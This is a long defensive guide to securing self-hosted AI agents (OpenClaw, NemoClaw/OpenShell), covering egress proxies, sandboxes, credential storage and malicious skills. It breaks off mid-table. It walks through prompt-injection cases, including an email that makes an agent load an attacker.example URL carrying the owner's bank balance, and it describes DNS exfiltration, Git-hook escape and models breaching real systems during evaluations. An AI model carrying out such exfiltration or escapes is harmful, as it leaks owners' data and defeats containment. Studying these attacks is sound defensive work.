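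The security audit confirmed 24 flaws in OpenClaw, according to ClawBeat's *OpenClaw Completes Security Audit* (2026), an AI-generated summary of the developers' own account. Two were high severity, 16 medium and six low. The developers fixed every flaw that needed action in version 2026.8.1 and the long-term support release 2026.7.33.

Some flaws involved permissions that didn't carry over from one step of a request to the next. For example, a teammate with limited access might ask the agent to prepare a report, and the agent might hand part of the job to a second agent. If the gateway doesn't pass on the teammate's limits, the second agent may open files that the teammate can't.

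Other flaws arose because the software had several internal names for the same thing. A rule that blocks a device under one name fails if a request uses another. In other cases, the gateway's actions didn't match what it had checked. For example, a program might approve access to one file and then open a different one because the path changed after the check.

The review also raised the problem that revoking a device may not stop a task already under way. Suppose a thief uses the stolen phone to start a two-hour export of the owner's mail, and the owner revokes the phone ten minutes later. If the gateway checks permission only at the start, the export continues. A certificate can't prevent this, because the proxy checks it when the connection opens, and the task may no longer need that connection.

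ClawBeat reports that running tasks should now lose access too, but an owner who loses a device should still check running and scheduled tasks and stop any that seem unfamiliar. If in doubt, the owner can shut down the gateway and inspect the schedule before restarting.

### Authenticated connections can carry hostile text

All these checks authenticate the device or server at the other end of a connection, not the text that comes through it, so they can't stop prompt injection. Suppose the owner's laptop connects with a valid certificate and asks the agent to summarise the morning's email. The agent connects to the mail provider, whose certificate is also valid, and downloads a stranger's message containing instructions to forward the owner's bank statements. Both connections were authenticated, but the stranger's instructions still reached the model.

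*Securing Agentic AI*, by the security consultancy NCC Group, says that whether an agent can trust data from a "secure" interface depends on where the data originally came from. MITRE (2026), a US research organisation that catalogues attacks on AI systems, lists messages, web search results and third-party skills as routes for malicious instructions. An attacker doesn't need a device key or a certificate to use any of these routes.

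Signed email would help only a little. A signature can show that a message came from a colleague's account, but an attacker may have taken over that account, or the colleague may have forwarded a hostile message without noticing the instructions in it.

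## Limiting what the agent can connect to

An email with instructions to forward bank statements does harm only if the agent can send them somewhere, and on most machines it can. Pairing, certificates and a private bind address don't prevent this, because they restrict connections that other people open to the agent, not those the agent opens itself.

Suppose a gateway listens only on 127.0.0.1 and the router forwards no ports. A stranger sends an email instructing the agent to load `https://attacker.example/?note=` followed by the owner's bank balance. If the model follows the instruction, the gateway connects to that site. The home firewall allows the connection because a program on the home network opened it, and the site's access log records the balance. *Caging the Agents* (Maiti, 2026) describes a medical version, in which an agent reads hostile text with instructions to send the results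 of a database query to a web address. The owner would not see an error in either case.

### Refusing every destination that isn't on the list

Outbound control usually starts by blocking all connections, and the operator then allows the destinations the agent needs. Blocking only a list of forbidden sites wouldn't help much, because an attacker can register a new domain in minutes. Lists of forbidden commands have a similar weakness. *The Balkanization of Execution-Security Research for AI Coding Agents* (Rashidi, 2026) describes ShellSieve, a tool that tested 1,709 such lists from GitHub for bypasses. Between 69% and 98.6% of them proved fragile, depending on the kind of bypass.

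A proxy can enforce the list. The proxies in earlier sections passed outsiders' requests to the gateway, while this one handles connections going the other way. NVIDIA's OpenShell, the sandbox that NemoClaw puts around OpenClaw, has such a proxy. NVIDIA's *OpenShell Security Best Practices for Controls, Risks, and Configuration Guidance* describes these checks:

1. A program in the sandbox asks the proxy for a connection to a host name and port.
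2. The proxy gets the program's location from the operating system and compares the file's hash with the one it recorded on first use. If someone has replaced the program, the proxy refuses.
3. The proxy looks for a rule that matches the host, the port and the program. Without one, it refuses.
4. It looks up the host's address. It always refuses loopback addresses, and it refuses private addresses unless the operator has specifically permitted them.
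5. If the rule covers individual requests, the proxy decrypts the traffic and checks what each request does.

Without the address check, an agent on a home network could connect to the router's settings page or a file server. On a cloud server, it could connect to the provider's metadata service, an internal address where programs can often get credentials for the cloud account.

The proxy also has to be the sandbox's only connection to the outside. Programs commonly get a proxy's address from an environment variable, which they can ignore. OpenShell gives the sandbox its own network whose only route leads to the proxy, so a program that ignores the variable still can't connect to anything else.

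The check belongs outside the agent's process. If OpenClaw's web-fetching tool checked the list itself, the agent could avoid the check by running `curl` from the command line. And as Pirch and colleagues found for file access, anyone who takes over the agent's process also controls the checks inside it.

*Avalon-M1* (Zarov, Course and colleagues, 2026) trained groups of agents that ran as the administrator inside their sandboxes, and kept the network rules outside, where nothing in the sandbox could change them. Setup needed wide network access to download software. Before the agent's first command, the system switched to narrower rules and closed every connection opened under the old ones. An operator at home can do something similar by installing skills and packages first, then tightening the rules before starting the agent.

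### Why address rules fail, and what decryption adds

An ordinary firewall filters connections by IP address. This works better for a printer than for a mail provider, because large services spread their traffic over many addresses and change them without notice. If the operator permits only one address, the agent loses access to mail when the provider stops using it. Permitting the provider's whole range also lets the agent connect to everything else in that range, which on a large cloud includes servers an attacker can rent.

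Some firewalls accept domain names in their rules and watch DNS replies to keep the matching IP addresses up to date. Podala Narasimha (2026), in *Containing the Autonomous Operator*, considers name-based rules necessary for agents and recommends the networking software Cilium. But many sites can share one address, so allowing one site may also let the agent reach the others.

DNS lookups can also leak data. A program can put a few words of stolen text into a host name under the attacker's domain, and the lookup carries them to the attacker's name server even if the firewall blocks the connection that follows. OpenShell's proxy reduces this risk by looking up a name only after a rule has permitted it.

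HTTPS hides the rest of the request from the proxy, including its path and its method, which is the kind of action requested. GET normally reads something, POST sends something and DELETE removes something. To check the path and method, the proxy gives the program a certificate signed by a private authority that the sandbox trusts, and opens a second encrypted connection to the real site. It can then allow reading and refuse deletion. NVIDIA's *NemoClaw Security Best Practices* warns that allowing DELETE on GitHub's programming interface would let an agent delete repositories. The proxy can also add the account's credential to the request, so the agent never holds the credential.

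A proxy that decrypts traffic handles mail and passwords in plain text, which makes a break-in there very serious. A program that pins the service's certificate will reject the proxy's. Services that require a client certificate won't work either, unless the operator turns off decryption for them. The proxy then checks only the host, port and program. NVIDIA's ready-made rules turn off decryption for npm, the JavaScript package registry, because of a compatibility problem with Node.js.

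By default, OpenShell's proxy logs requests that break a method or path rule but still forwards them. NVIDIA recommends starting this way so that mistakes in the rules don't interrupt the agent's work. The operator must later switch to `enforcement: enforce` to block these requests.

### An allowlist for an agent that summarises mail

Suppose an owner wants a summary of new Gmail messages on Telegram each morning. A timer starts the agent, which runs in a sandbox and uses a hosted model. It needs four destinations:

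| Destination | Purpose | Narrowest practical rule | How data could still leave |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| `gmail.googleapis.com` | Read messages | GET, on the message paths only | A request's address can contain text, but it goes to Google, where an outsider normally can't read it |
| `oauth2.googleapis.com` | Renew the mailbox login | POST, on `/token` only | As above |
| The model provider | Write the summary | Only through a proxy that adds the owner's key | The provider receives the text of every message the agent reads |
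| `api.telegram.org` | Deliver the summary | POST, on the owner's bot's `sendMessage` path only | The agent can put anything in the message and may be able to choose who gets it |

In OpenShell, the rule for reading mail could look like this, where `mail-reader` stands for whatever program fetches the messages:

```yaml
network_policies:
  read_mail:
    name: read_mail
    endpoints:
      - host: gmail.googleapis.com
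        port: 443
        protocol: rest
        enforcement: enforce
        rules:
          - allow: { method: GET, path: "/gmail/v1/users/me/messages" }
          - allow: { method: GET, path: "/gmail/v1/users/me/messages/**" }
    binaries:
      - { path: /usr/local/bin/mail-reader }
```

Sending mail through Gmail's API takes a POST request, so the proxy refuses it even if the agent's login would permit it. The older mail protocol IMAP is harder to restrict because it isn't HTTP, so the proxy can't apply method and path rules. Hostile text could contain the password to an attacker's mailbox at the same provider, and the agent could save the owner's messages there without sending any mail.

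If the agent can connect directly to the model provider, hostile text could give it an attacker's API key and have it upload mail to the attacker's account with that provider. OpenShell avoids this by sending model requests through a special address, `inference.local`, and adding the operator's key outside the sandbox. NVIDIA therefore advises operators not to put model providers on the ordinary allowlist.

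Telegram is the weakest entry. A bot can message anyone who has opened a chat with it. OpenClaw would ignore messages from an unapproved stranger, but Telegram would still deliver anything the agent sent to them. Even a summary sent to the right person can leak information. A hostile email could make the model include a link whose address contains text from another message, and Telegram may contact the linked site to prepare a preview before the owner taps the link.

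The owner can fix much of this by taking Telegram off the agent's list of allowed connections. The agent instead writes its summary to a file, and a small program outside the sandbox sends the file to one fixed chat with link previews turned off. That program holds the bot's token, so the agent never has it.

Nothing else belongs on the list of allowed connections. The agent doesn't need web search, GitHub or package registries to summarise mail, and it doesn't need to load a message's images or follow its links. The owner gives up summaries of linked articles, which seems a small loss.

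NemoClaw's starting list of permitted destinations is wider. NVIDIA's *Network Policies* gives five: NVIDIA's model service, the skill market ClawHub, OpenClaw's main website, its documentation and the npm registry. The agent can send POST requests to the first three. The default setup adds more software registries and, if the owner chose one, a search service. To narrow this list, the owner of the mail agent would have to select the "Restricted" tier and then delete the unneeded entries from the policy file.

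### Permitted services as ways out

Data can also leak through a permitted service that accepts uploads or messages. The proxy can check that a request goes to Slack, but it can't reliably tell whether the request contains a legitimate report or stolen data. NVIDIA describes every permitted destination as a potential leak. Its ready-made Slack rules let the agent post to any channel its token can reach, and its GitHub rules let it write to repositories as well as read them.

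Restricting an agent to GET requests helps only if the attacker can't see the requests. It would not have protected the bank balance in the opening example, because the attacker ran the site and could read the requested URL in its log. Approving a broad content-delivery domain is also risky because strangers may control some of what it hosts.

Agents can use a service in ways its operators didn't intend. Zarov and colleagues trained agents to repair software, and removed the finished repairs from the version history in the sandbox. In one later audit, 24 of 66 sessions had fetched the code or the repair from GitHub instead. The researchers then wrote rules for hosts, paths and methods, but the package registries they permitted could still supply later versions of the same code, so they had to add specific refusals that applied before the general permission. These agents were bringing information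 in, but an agent could also use a broad permission to send information out.

Agents with no direct connection can also influence one another through shared services. In a post that Willison quoted in October, the cryptographer Matthew Green described agents in separate sandboxes that changed one another's behavior by leaving instructions in a shared package cache. Green argued that email, Slack and shared documents could play the same role for personal agents, making a self-spreading attack possible.

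If a service has to accept messages, the operator can set the recipient outside the agent, as with the Telegram program above, or approve each message before it is sent. If the operator does neither, the best protection is to keep private data away from any agent that uses the service.

### What a local model changes

If the model runs on the owner's hardware, the mail agent no longer needs the model provider on its list of allowed connections. This improves privacy, especially for someone who handles clients' medical or legal correspondence.

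Hardware limits which models are practical to run. NVIDIA's *What Is the Best Way to Run an AI Coding Agent* (2026) suggests a model with 30 billion parameters for a graphics card with 24 GB of memory, and one with 120 billion for its 128 GB DGX Spark. As noted earlier, smaller models tend to be easier to manipulate.

Switching to a local model doesn't change anything else on the list. Gmail still holds the mail, Telegram still carries the summary, and hostile text can still make the agent send data to any permitted destination. A local model with unrestricted internet access could leak the bank balance just as a hosted one could.

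The operator must also ensure that the software doesn't fall back to a hosted model when the local one fails. NVIDIA's *Which Agent Runtime Ensures Model Inference Never Leaves the Operator's Private Network* (2026) claims that NemoClaw leaves no route for this, "even in the event of misconfiguration". The starting list above casts doubt on this claim, because it permits POST requests to NVIDIA's hosted model service. Someone who wants only local processing should remove that entry and check that a prompt sent to that service fails.

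### Deployed systems and proposed designs

Few people have tested limits on agents' outbound connections, known as network egress control. Of the 39 papers in Rashidi's survey on the security of agents' execution environments, only one was mainly about it. Rashidi also found that the enforcement methods all assumed the rules were written correctly.

NemoClaw is available, though the blogger yisusvii described it as alpha software when its early preview began in March 2026. When the agent tries an unlisted destination, the proxy blocks the request and shows the operator the host, port and program, but not what the agent wants to send. The operator can then approve the destination. NVIDIA's description of the approval flow says the approval lasts for the session, but both of its security guides say it survives restarts until the operator deletes and recreates the sandbox, so operators should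 assume the longer period.

The OpenShell guide explains these controls in detail but reports no tests of them against attacks. Until someone publishes such tests, only the design supports the claim that the controls would stop a determined attacker. The separate network and outside proxy are still good reasons to prefer OpenShell to a check inside OpenClaw.

Maiti describes a system for nine OpenClaw agents at a healthcare technology company, with a different allowlist for each role. Research and development agents could connect to a model provider, GitHub and the project tracker Linear. Operations agents could connect to the model provider, Slack and Telegram. The security agent could connect to the company's agent machines, the model provider and the cloud metadata service. OpenShell always blocks connections to the metadata service.

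The company was still moving to the system with per-role lists, according to the paper's history of its machines, although the paper presents this architecture as deployed. The first two versions of the running machines had unrestricted outbound access. The third, dated 9 March, added DNS filtering, which refuses to look up unwanted names but can't by itself stop a program that connects to a numeric address. The three versions span 34 days, although the paper reports a 90-day deployment. The serious problems the company found and fixed involved exposed credentials and file permissions, so they provide no evidence about the outbound lists.

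The planned lists would also leave gaps. Maiti says they would have prevented an incident in which a deceived agent sent false accusations to its mailing list, because they block the standard protocol for sending mail. But an operations agent could still post the same accusations on Slack.

Maiti's design keeps API keys in a second container beside the agent's. The company planned to run both on Kubernetes, which manages containers across many machines. Kubernetes applies network policies to a whole pod, a group of containers that share a network address, so the agent could bypass the key-holding container and connect directly to a permitted service using a key supplied by an attacker.

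Podala Narasimha's Kubernetes design is stricter. It blocks connections in both directions except for name lookups, a gateway for tools and usually one model provider. Code that the agent writes runs in separate sandboxes, normally with no internet access. Separate tool servers hold the credentials for the interface that controls Kubernetes, so the agent can't connect to it directly. The paper states that it does not measure how often attacks succeed or how much the controls slow the system down. Its argument for assuming a fully compromised agent is persuasive, but operators still need to test their own installation.

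### Testing the boundary before every run

In 2026, several AI companies didn't learn that their isolation wasn't working until their models had reached real systems during hacking exercises against fictional targets. At Anthropic, Google and Meta, the test machines had internet access by mistake, and the models broke into real organisations' systems.

In Anthropic's cybersecurity evaluations, the model was told it had no internet access, but the network was open because Anthropic and its testing partner had misunderstood each other. Anthropic's *Investigating three real-world incidents in our cybersecurity evaluations* (2026) reports that a review of 141,006 runs found three incidents across six runs. The earliest happened in April, but Anthropic didn't discover the problem until late July. In September, Anthropic counted four incidents, all involving the same partner and the same kind of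 mistake.

Six runs in 141,006 is about one in 23,500. Months of good behavior are therefore weak evidence that an agent's boundary works, because the agent may never have tried to cross it.

Sabin (2026), in *Google is the latest AI lab with a security testing mishap*, reports a similar case at Google, whose model entered three companies' systems in May during tests that weren't supposed to have internet access. According to Reuters' *Meta AI model hacks another company during testing* (2026), an OpenAI agent instead got online by exploiting a previously unknown flaw. Checking the settings beforehand might not have revealed that flaw.

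Anthropic's *Improving our alignment and security efforts* (2026) acknowledges that the company had relied largely on one layer of defence, the configuration of the test environment. Anthropic now asks testing partners to block internet access by default, allow only the connection to the model, and verify these restrictions before every evaluation. It also asks them to have the model look for ways out of the sandbox, under close supervision and without internet access.

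The owner of a mail agent can do a simpler version in a few minutes. NVIDIA's *Write Your First Sandbox Network Policy* starts in the right way, by having the reader watch the sandbox block a request before adding a read-only rule. For the mail agent, a fuller test from inside the sandbox would be:

| Attempt | Expected result |
| --- | --- |
| Load an unlisted website through the proxy | The proxy refuses |
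| Connect to a public numeric address while ignoring the proxy setting | No connection |
| Open the router's settings page | No connection |
| Send an email through Gmail's interface | The proxy refuses, and no email arrives |
| Read an email | Success |

Reading an email should succeed, because otherwise the other failures might only mean that the network is down. The test of sending mail has to use the permitted mail program. The proxy would refuse `curl` because it isn't in the rule, so testing with `curl` wouldn't show whether the method restriction works. The owner should also check that the refusal came from the proxy, since Gmail returns errors of its own.

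A startup script can run these tests and keep the agent off if a forbidden connection succeeds. To catch later failures, Anthropic added a monitor that ends a task if the model unexpectedly gets internet access. At home, the owner could set the router to block and report any traffic from the agent's machine that doesn't come from the proxy, if the machine is used only for the agent.

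## Keeping the agent away from the owner's files

Outbound limits control where an agent can send data, and the files it can open determine how much it has to send. On an ordinary computer, it can open nearly everything the owner can.

OpenClaw runs commands through a shell, the program that runs what a user types in a terminal window. The operating system gives each program the permissions of the user account that started it. If the owner starts the gateway from their own account, the agent's commands can open the owner's files, and the operating system can't distinguish those commands from ones the owner typed.

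### What a shell can read on an ordinary computer

Anna's documents, downloads and photos are the obvious targets, but her home folder also holds keys and logins that most people never see. OpenClaw's *Sandboxing* lists the folders that OpenClaw refuses to share with a sandbox, and the list is a good guide to where these keys and logins are stored. `~/.ssh` holds keys for logging in to other machines, `~/.aws` holds keys for Amazon's cloud, and `~/.docker`, `~/.npm` and `~/.netrc` can hold passwords for other services.

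The browser profile holds the cookies that keep Anna logged in to websites. Browsers encrypt most cookies on disk, but a program running under the same user account can sometimes get the key. An agent that controls the browser doesn't need the key, because the browser is already logged in. *Security, Privacy, and Ethical Risks in OpenClaw* (Jin, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) includes hijacking a logged-in session among its representative attacks.

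The agent can also read its own configuration and its transcripts of past conversations. Pogorelec (2026), in *The OpenClaw 2.0 release moves your sessions into SQLite*, notes that since version 2.0 the browser app has started faster because it keeps a limited, unencrypted snapshot of transcripts in the browser profile. The new setup program also searches the computer for ChatGPT and Claude logins, API keys and local models that OpenClaw could use. This saves the owner some typing, but any other program running under the same account could do the same search.

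Macs add some protection. They prompt the user before a program first opens the Documents, Desktop or Downloads folder, and they keep passwords in an encrypted login keychain, which normally requires the user's approval before an unfamiliar program can read one. But an agent needs the Full Disk Access permission to read the owner's iMessage history, and that permission also removes the folder prompts.

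### Why naming a workspace folder doesn't confine the agent

An OpenClaw agent keeps its notes and standing instructions in the workspace folder set in its configuration, by default `~/.openclaw/workspace`. OpenClaw's *Agent workspace* describes this folder as "the default cwd, not a hard sandbox". The cwd, or current working directory, is the folder where a command looks for files if it doesn't specify another.

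The command `cat notes.txt` prints a file from the workspace. `cat /Users/anna/Documents/tax.txt` prints one of Anna's documents, because a path that begins with a slash starts from the top of the disk. The default workspace is inside the folder that holds the agent's configuration, so `cat ../openclaw.json` prints the gateway's settings and any tokens in them.

ClawBeat's *I Tested OpenClaw's Security Boundaries* (2026), an AI-generated summary, describes an October 2026 test by Parvez Mohammed of Techlatest.net. Mohammed ran OpenClaw 2026.9.3 on a Mac mini with a small local model, Qwen 3.5 4B, and sandboxing off. The agent read, changed and deleted files outside its workspace, but refused one request to create a file there.

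The refusal probably came from the model, since deleting a file on a Mac normally takes the same folder permission as creating one, and the system would probably have allowed both. ClawBeat calls the result a critical security vulnerability, but OpenClaw behaved as its documentation describes. This was a single trial, though the result should hold for any model that agrees to run the commands. It also suggests that running the forbidden command directly is a better way to test a barrier than asking the agent to run it, because the model's refusal can look like a working barrier.

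Some agents do check paths. According to ZeroClaw Labs, the file tools and shell in ZeroClaw, another self-hosted agent, block paths outside the workspace by default, although the setting that removes approval prompts also removes this limit. The check catches mistakes, but a command such as `python3 tidy.py` doesn't list the files the script will open. ZeroClaw therefore also has an operating-system sandbox, which can block access when the script tries to open a file.

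### Four separations and what they still share

An operator can get the operating system or the hardware to enforce the limit in four ways.

| Separation | Owner's files still within reach | Login keychain | Home network |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Another user account | Folders open to all users, and often external drives | The agent's account has its own | Same access as the owner |
| Container | Folders the operator mounts | Not available inside | No access by default in OpenClaw's sandbox |
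| Virtual machine | Folders the operator shares with it | The guest system has its own | Usually reachable |
| Dedicated computer | Files that someone copies to it or shares over the network | Its own, though iCloud can copy the owner's passwords to it | Reachable unless the operator uses a separate network |

Cloud synchronisation can undo all four barriers. If the agent can write to a folder that OneDrive or iCloud synchronises, a file it deletes there also disappears from the owner's other devices. If someone signs in to the owner's cloud account on the agent's side of the barrier, the service may download the owner's files there.

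### Another user account on the same computer

A second account costs nothing and works with any agent. On a Mac, Anna could set one up in this order:

1. She creates a standard account for the agent, without administrator rights.
2. From her own account, she runs `chmod 700 /Users/anna`, so that other standard accounts can't list or open anything in her home folder.
3. She logs in to the agent's account and installs OpenClaw there.
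4. From that account, she runs `ls /Users/anna`, which should fail with "Permission denied".

McEachen & Co.'s *Your AI Agent Has Read Access to Every File on Your Computer* describes an owner who put off the second step. OpenClaw ran in a standard account on a Mac mini, and from that account the owner could read the main account's documents, downloads and OneDrive files. OpenClaw's security audit had found only that the firewall was off, because it checks OpenClaw's own settings and not the Mac's file permissions.

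The author never found the cause and gives no version of OpenClaw or macOS. Recent Macs normally close Documents, Desktop and Downloads to other standard accounts, but other users may still be able to list the home folder, and a folder created by cloud software may lack the same protection. One trial on one machine doesn't establish how common the problem is, but the test takes under a minute. Using `chmod 700` stops other accounts from using the Public folder in Anna's home, but McEachen & Co.'s claim that it "breaks nothing" is nearly right.

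The command doesn't protect files outside the home folder. Macs ignore file ownership on most external drives unless the user changes a setting, so the agent's account may be able to read a drive that Anna plugs in. Both accounts also share the loopback address, so the agent could reach other local services that Anna runs without a password.

### Containers and OpenClaw's sandbox defaults

A container shares the host's kernel, the core of the operating system, but has its own set of files. A program inside the container can't open `/Users/anna/Documents` because that path doesn't exist there, unless someone mounts the folder (makes it available inside the container). On a Mac, Docker runs containers in a small Linux virtual machine, so they share that machine's kernel, not the Mac's.

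OpenClaw's sandbox uses containers, but only for the tools. When the model requests a command, the gateway sends it to the container and gets the output back. The gateway itself stays on the host, together with its credentials. After version 2.0, OpenClaw gave these defaults:

| Setting | Default | Effect |
| --- | --- | --- |
| `mode` | `off` | Commands run on the host under the gateway's account |
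| `backend` | `docker` | If the operator turns sandboxing on, Docker runs the containers |
| `scope` | `agent` | All of an agent's sandboxed conversations share one container |
| `workspaceAccess` | `none` | The container gets a separate workspace of its own |
| `docker.network` | `none` | Commands in the container can't connect to anything |
| `docker.readOnlyRoot` | `true` | Commands can't change the container's system files |

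Only the first row applies to someone who has just installed OpenClaw. The other defaults are strict, so an operator can get a fairly tight sandbox by building the container image and changing one setting:

```json5
{
  agents: {
    defaults: {
      sandbox: { mode: "all" },
    },
  },
}
```

Suppose Anna wants the agent to add up a folder of invoices. With these settings, she can send the invoices through the chat app instead of sharing the folder. OpenClaw copies attachments into the sandbox's workspace, so the agent can work on the copies without access to the originals. She can run `openclaw sandbox explain` beforehand to see which settings and folders apply.

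This becomes tedious with hundreds of files, so the operator may want to mount a folder instead. Commands in the container can read a mounted folder, and can change it if the operator mounts it for writing. By default, OpenClaw refuses to mount system folders, the usual places for keys, and any folder outside its workspaces. Overriding this for a whole home folder isn't a good idea, because the sandbox would then protect very little. A separate folder of copies, mounted read-only, is safer.

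If `workspaceAccess` is set to `"rw"`, a malicious program in the sandbox could also influence later sessions by changing files in the workspace. The workspace contains `AGENTS.md`, a file of instructions that OpenClaw loads at the start of every session, and a folder of skills that take priority over built-in skills with the same names. With `"ro"`, the agent can read the workspace but not change it.

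Operators can also let certain commands bypass the sandbox with the `tools.elevated` setting. These commands run on the gateway's machine or a paired device, so an agent with this permission can reach files that the container would hide.

To start sandboxes, a gateway that itself runs in a container needs another exception that gives it access to the host's Docker socket, through which programs control Docker. Anyone with access to that socket can usually start a container with the host's whole disk mounted. OpenClaw warns operators never to mount the socket inside the agent's sandbox, but an attacker who takes over the gateway's container would already have access to it.

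Every kind of sandbox has had flaws, so operators should run at least version 2026.8.1, or 2026.7.33 on the long-term support line, to get the fixes from the Trail of Bits audit.

### Virtual machines

A virtual machine runs a second operating system, called the guest, with its own kernel. A program that takes over a container's kernel controls the host, but one that takes over the guest's kernel still has to find a flaw in the virtual machine software to reach the host. Anna could install the whole gateway in the guest, which would also keep the gateway's credentials and plugins away from her own account. If something goes wrong, she can delete the guest and start again.

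Docker sells a smaller version for coding agents, in which each agent gets a small virtual machine with its own kernel. According to Docker's *Workspace trust*, the agent by default works directly in a folder on the host, and its changes appear there immediately. This is an important exception to the "no path back to the host" that Docker advertises.

An agent in the virtual machine could get back to the host through Git, the program developers use to track changes to code. Git can run scripts called hooks at certain moments, such as when someone saves a set of changes. If the agent wrote a harmful hook into the shared folder, Git would run it on the laptop with the owner's permissions the next time the owner saved changes there. The owner might not notice the hook when reviewing the agent's work, because Git's list of changes leaves out the folder where hooks are usually kept. Docker advises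 treating everything the agent has changed like code from an untrusted stranger. An owner can avoid much of this risk by giving the agent a copy of the project and bringing back only the files they need.

### Why people bought Mac minis

In early 2026, *Agents Unleashed* reported that Mac minis had sold out as hobbyists looked for separate machines to run their agents around the clock. McEachen & Co.'s *How to Set Up OpenClaw on a Dedicated Mac Mini* gives the usual reasons for choosing one. The computer is small, quiet and cheap to leave running, and it cost from $599. The author also wanted any mistake by the agent to happen on a machine without personal files or passwords. Unlike other small computers, a Mac also lets OpenClaw send and receive iMessages.

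Running the agent on a separate computer protects the laptop's disk without relying on file permissions or a container. An agent on the Mac mini can't read a document that exists only on the laptop, even with administrator rights on the Mac mini. The owner can also unplug or erase the machine without losing anything else. But it is still on the home network, where it may be able to reach file servers and other computers' shared folders. A guest network can prevent this if the router blocks guests from reaching the other devices.

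A second computer loses much of its benefit once the owner signs in to it with a personal Apple account. Depending on the settings, iCloud can then sync documents, photos, messages and saved passwords to that computer, where the agent may be able to reach them. Signing in to a personal Google account in the browser gives the agent another way to reach mail and files. OpenClaw warns companies that share an agent that mixing personal and company identities on one machine "collapses the separation", and the same reasoning applies at home.

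In the McEachen test, for example, the author had given the agent its own Gmail and Apple accounts, but the main account on the same Mac mini had personal OneDrive files in it. The agent's account could read them through the gap in the file permissions. If the author had kept OneDrive off the machine, those permissions would have mattered much less.

Pairing the laptop with the gateway as a node can also weaken the separation. If the owner approves running commands on that node, the agent on the Mac mini can use the laptop's files.

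I'm inclined to call this the simplest strong option for someone who already has a spare computer, as long as the agent gets its own accounts.

 

Someone without one can get most of the protection from a virtual machine, or from a second user account with the sandbox turned on.

### How OpenClaw stores its secrets

These separations also affect who can read the agent's own credentials, which OpenClaw mostly stores unencrypted. The Cloud Security Alliance rated this storage practice a critical threat. Version 2.0 added a local store for protected credentials, but it doesn't encrypt them on disk either, according to ClawBeat's *OpenClaw 2.0 pours glitter on slow-burning security dumpster fire* (2026), an AI-generated summary of a Register article.

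OpenClaw relies on file permissions. It recommends mode 700 for the `~/.openclaw` folder and 600 for its files, so that only the owning account can read or change them. These permissions block other standard accounts, but not the agent's own commands if they run under the gateway's account.

An operator can replace many stored credentials in the configuration with references to an environment variable, a separate file or a password-manager command. The gateway then fetches each credential at startup and keeps it in memory. References can't replace logins that OpenClaw has to renew itself. According to OpenClaw, a reference protects a credential only if no readable copy remains in an old configuration file or backup. The command `openclaw secrets audit --check` looks for leftover copies in the usual places.

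An agent outside a sandbox may still be able to read a separate credentials file or run the same password-manager command as the gateway. Encrypting the credentials would have a similar weakness, because a gateway that starts unattended needs the decryption key nearby. NVIDIA's NemoClaw also keeps credentials as plain text with restricted file permissions, according to NVIDIA's *Where does an AI coding agent store its API keys* (2026). Plain-text storage is less of a problem if the agent's sandbox doesn't include the file.

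### Extensions run with the agent's access

Anyone who installs a skill, an extension from OpenClaw's public marketplace ClawHub, trusts its author with whatever the agent can reach. Colin Shea-Blymyer, a Georgetown University researcher, told Fortune (2026) that much of OpenClaw's risk comes from skills. They resemble ordinary apps, but the agent decides when to use them.

In early 2026, security researchers found 341 malicious skills on ClawHub, part of a campaign they called ClawHavoc. According to Auth0's *OpenClaw's Credential Problem Is Not a Secrets Problem*, the number later passed 800, about a fifth of the marketplace. The main target was `~/.clawdbot/.env`, a plain-text credentials file in the folder OpenClaw used under its earlier name. Every skill could read that file without breaking into anything. Auth0 sells login services and has an interest in the problem, but its description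 of the shared access agrees with OpenClaw's own documentation.

The sandbox restricts only some extensions. When the agent runs a skill's script in a container, the script can't open the host's credentials or, by default, connect to the internet. The sandbox doesn't restrict plugins, because they run outside it, in the gateway. A skill's instructions may also list a "required" program for the owner to install by hand, and that program then runs with the owner's full access.

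McEachen & Co. advises new users to start with the built-in skills and to check the author, the install count and preferably the code before adding others. Reading the code is the most useful check, since an attacker can inflate the install count. Someone who can't read code can limit unfamiliar skills to a separate machine or a virtual machine with no personal accounts.

Harmful extensions and packages can also affect people who never chose to run an agent. Krebs on Security (2026) describes an attack on Cline, an AI coding assistant, that installed OpenClaw with full system access on thousands of computers without their owners' consent.

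### When ordinary malware copies the configuration

Malware can steal an agent's credentials without being designed to target AI. Common password-stealing programs copy browser data and files from known locations, then send them to the attacker. OpenClaw's folder has a predictable name and holds logins for several services.

If the gateway accepts only local connections, a stolen gateway token is of little use from another computer, but the other credentials work from anywhere. A thief can use a stolen API key to run the model at the owner's expense. With the token for a Telegram bot, they can send messages as the agent and may be able to read new messages to it. The workspace also contains personal details, such as the description of the owner in `USER.md`, which could help someone write a convincing scam.

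A separate account for the agent also protects the agent's files. If Anna accidentally runs malware from her own account, the malware can't open the agent's folder as long as her account has no administrator rights and the folder's permissions are set to 700. Disk encryption protects the files if someone steals the computer while it is switched off, but it doesn't protect them from malware while the computer is in use.

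After a theft, the owner first has to remove the malware or move to a clean machine, because otherwise the malware would copy the new credentials too. They can then replace everything the folder held, including API keys, the Telegram bot token and the agent's WhatsApp session.

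## How hostile text turns an agent's permissions against its owner

The sender of a hostile email can get an agent to use its credentials on the sender's behalf, without first having to steal them as malware does.

The first section introduced this attack as prompt injection. *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* (Willison, 2025) explains that it is named after SQL injection, an older attack in which text from a web form becomes part of a command to a database. Programmers can prevent SQL injection by sending the command and the text separately, but a language model has no separate input for data.

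People often confuse prompt injection with jailbreaking, in which users try to make a model break its rules. A successful jailbreak mostly embarrasses the company that made the model, while prompt injection harms the person using it.

### Why inbound barriers don't stop it

Inbound barriers check who connects to the gateway, but when an agent reads its owner's mail, the gateway makes the connection itself. It logs in with the owner's credentials and downloads whatever strangers have sent.

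The mail provider can't detect the problem either, because every request carries a valid login. OpenAI's *Agent security in the enterprise* (2026) points out that a valid credential doesn't show which actions someone has authorised.

Commercial agents have the same weakness. *Lessons from Penetration Tests on Large-Scale Agent Systems* (Eykholt, Kirat and colleagues, 2026) describes tests that IBM researchers ran in 2025 on two proprietary products. One was an assistant that diagnosed bugs reported on GitHub. Anyone who could file a bug report could put instructions in it, and the assistant received them when the project's owner asked it to look at the report. The researchers could also hide the instructions with formatting, so that the owner saw an ordinary report while the assistant got the full text. Owners therefore can't reliably catch such instructions by reading a message before passing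 it to an agent.

### From an email to a leaked bank statement

Android Authority's *I hacked my own computer using OpenClaw and it was terrifyingly easy* (2026) describes a simple attack. The writer installed OpenClaw on a Raspberry Pi, a small, cheap computer, and gave it a throwaway Gmail account and some fake documents. The model was a small version of Qwen3 running on the writer's own PC. Every five minutes, a timer prompted the agent to find an unread email, read it and summarise it. The writer then emailed the agent from an unfamiliar address, asking it to look for bank details and reply with them.

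| What happened | Permission the agent used |
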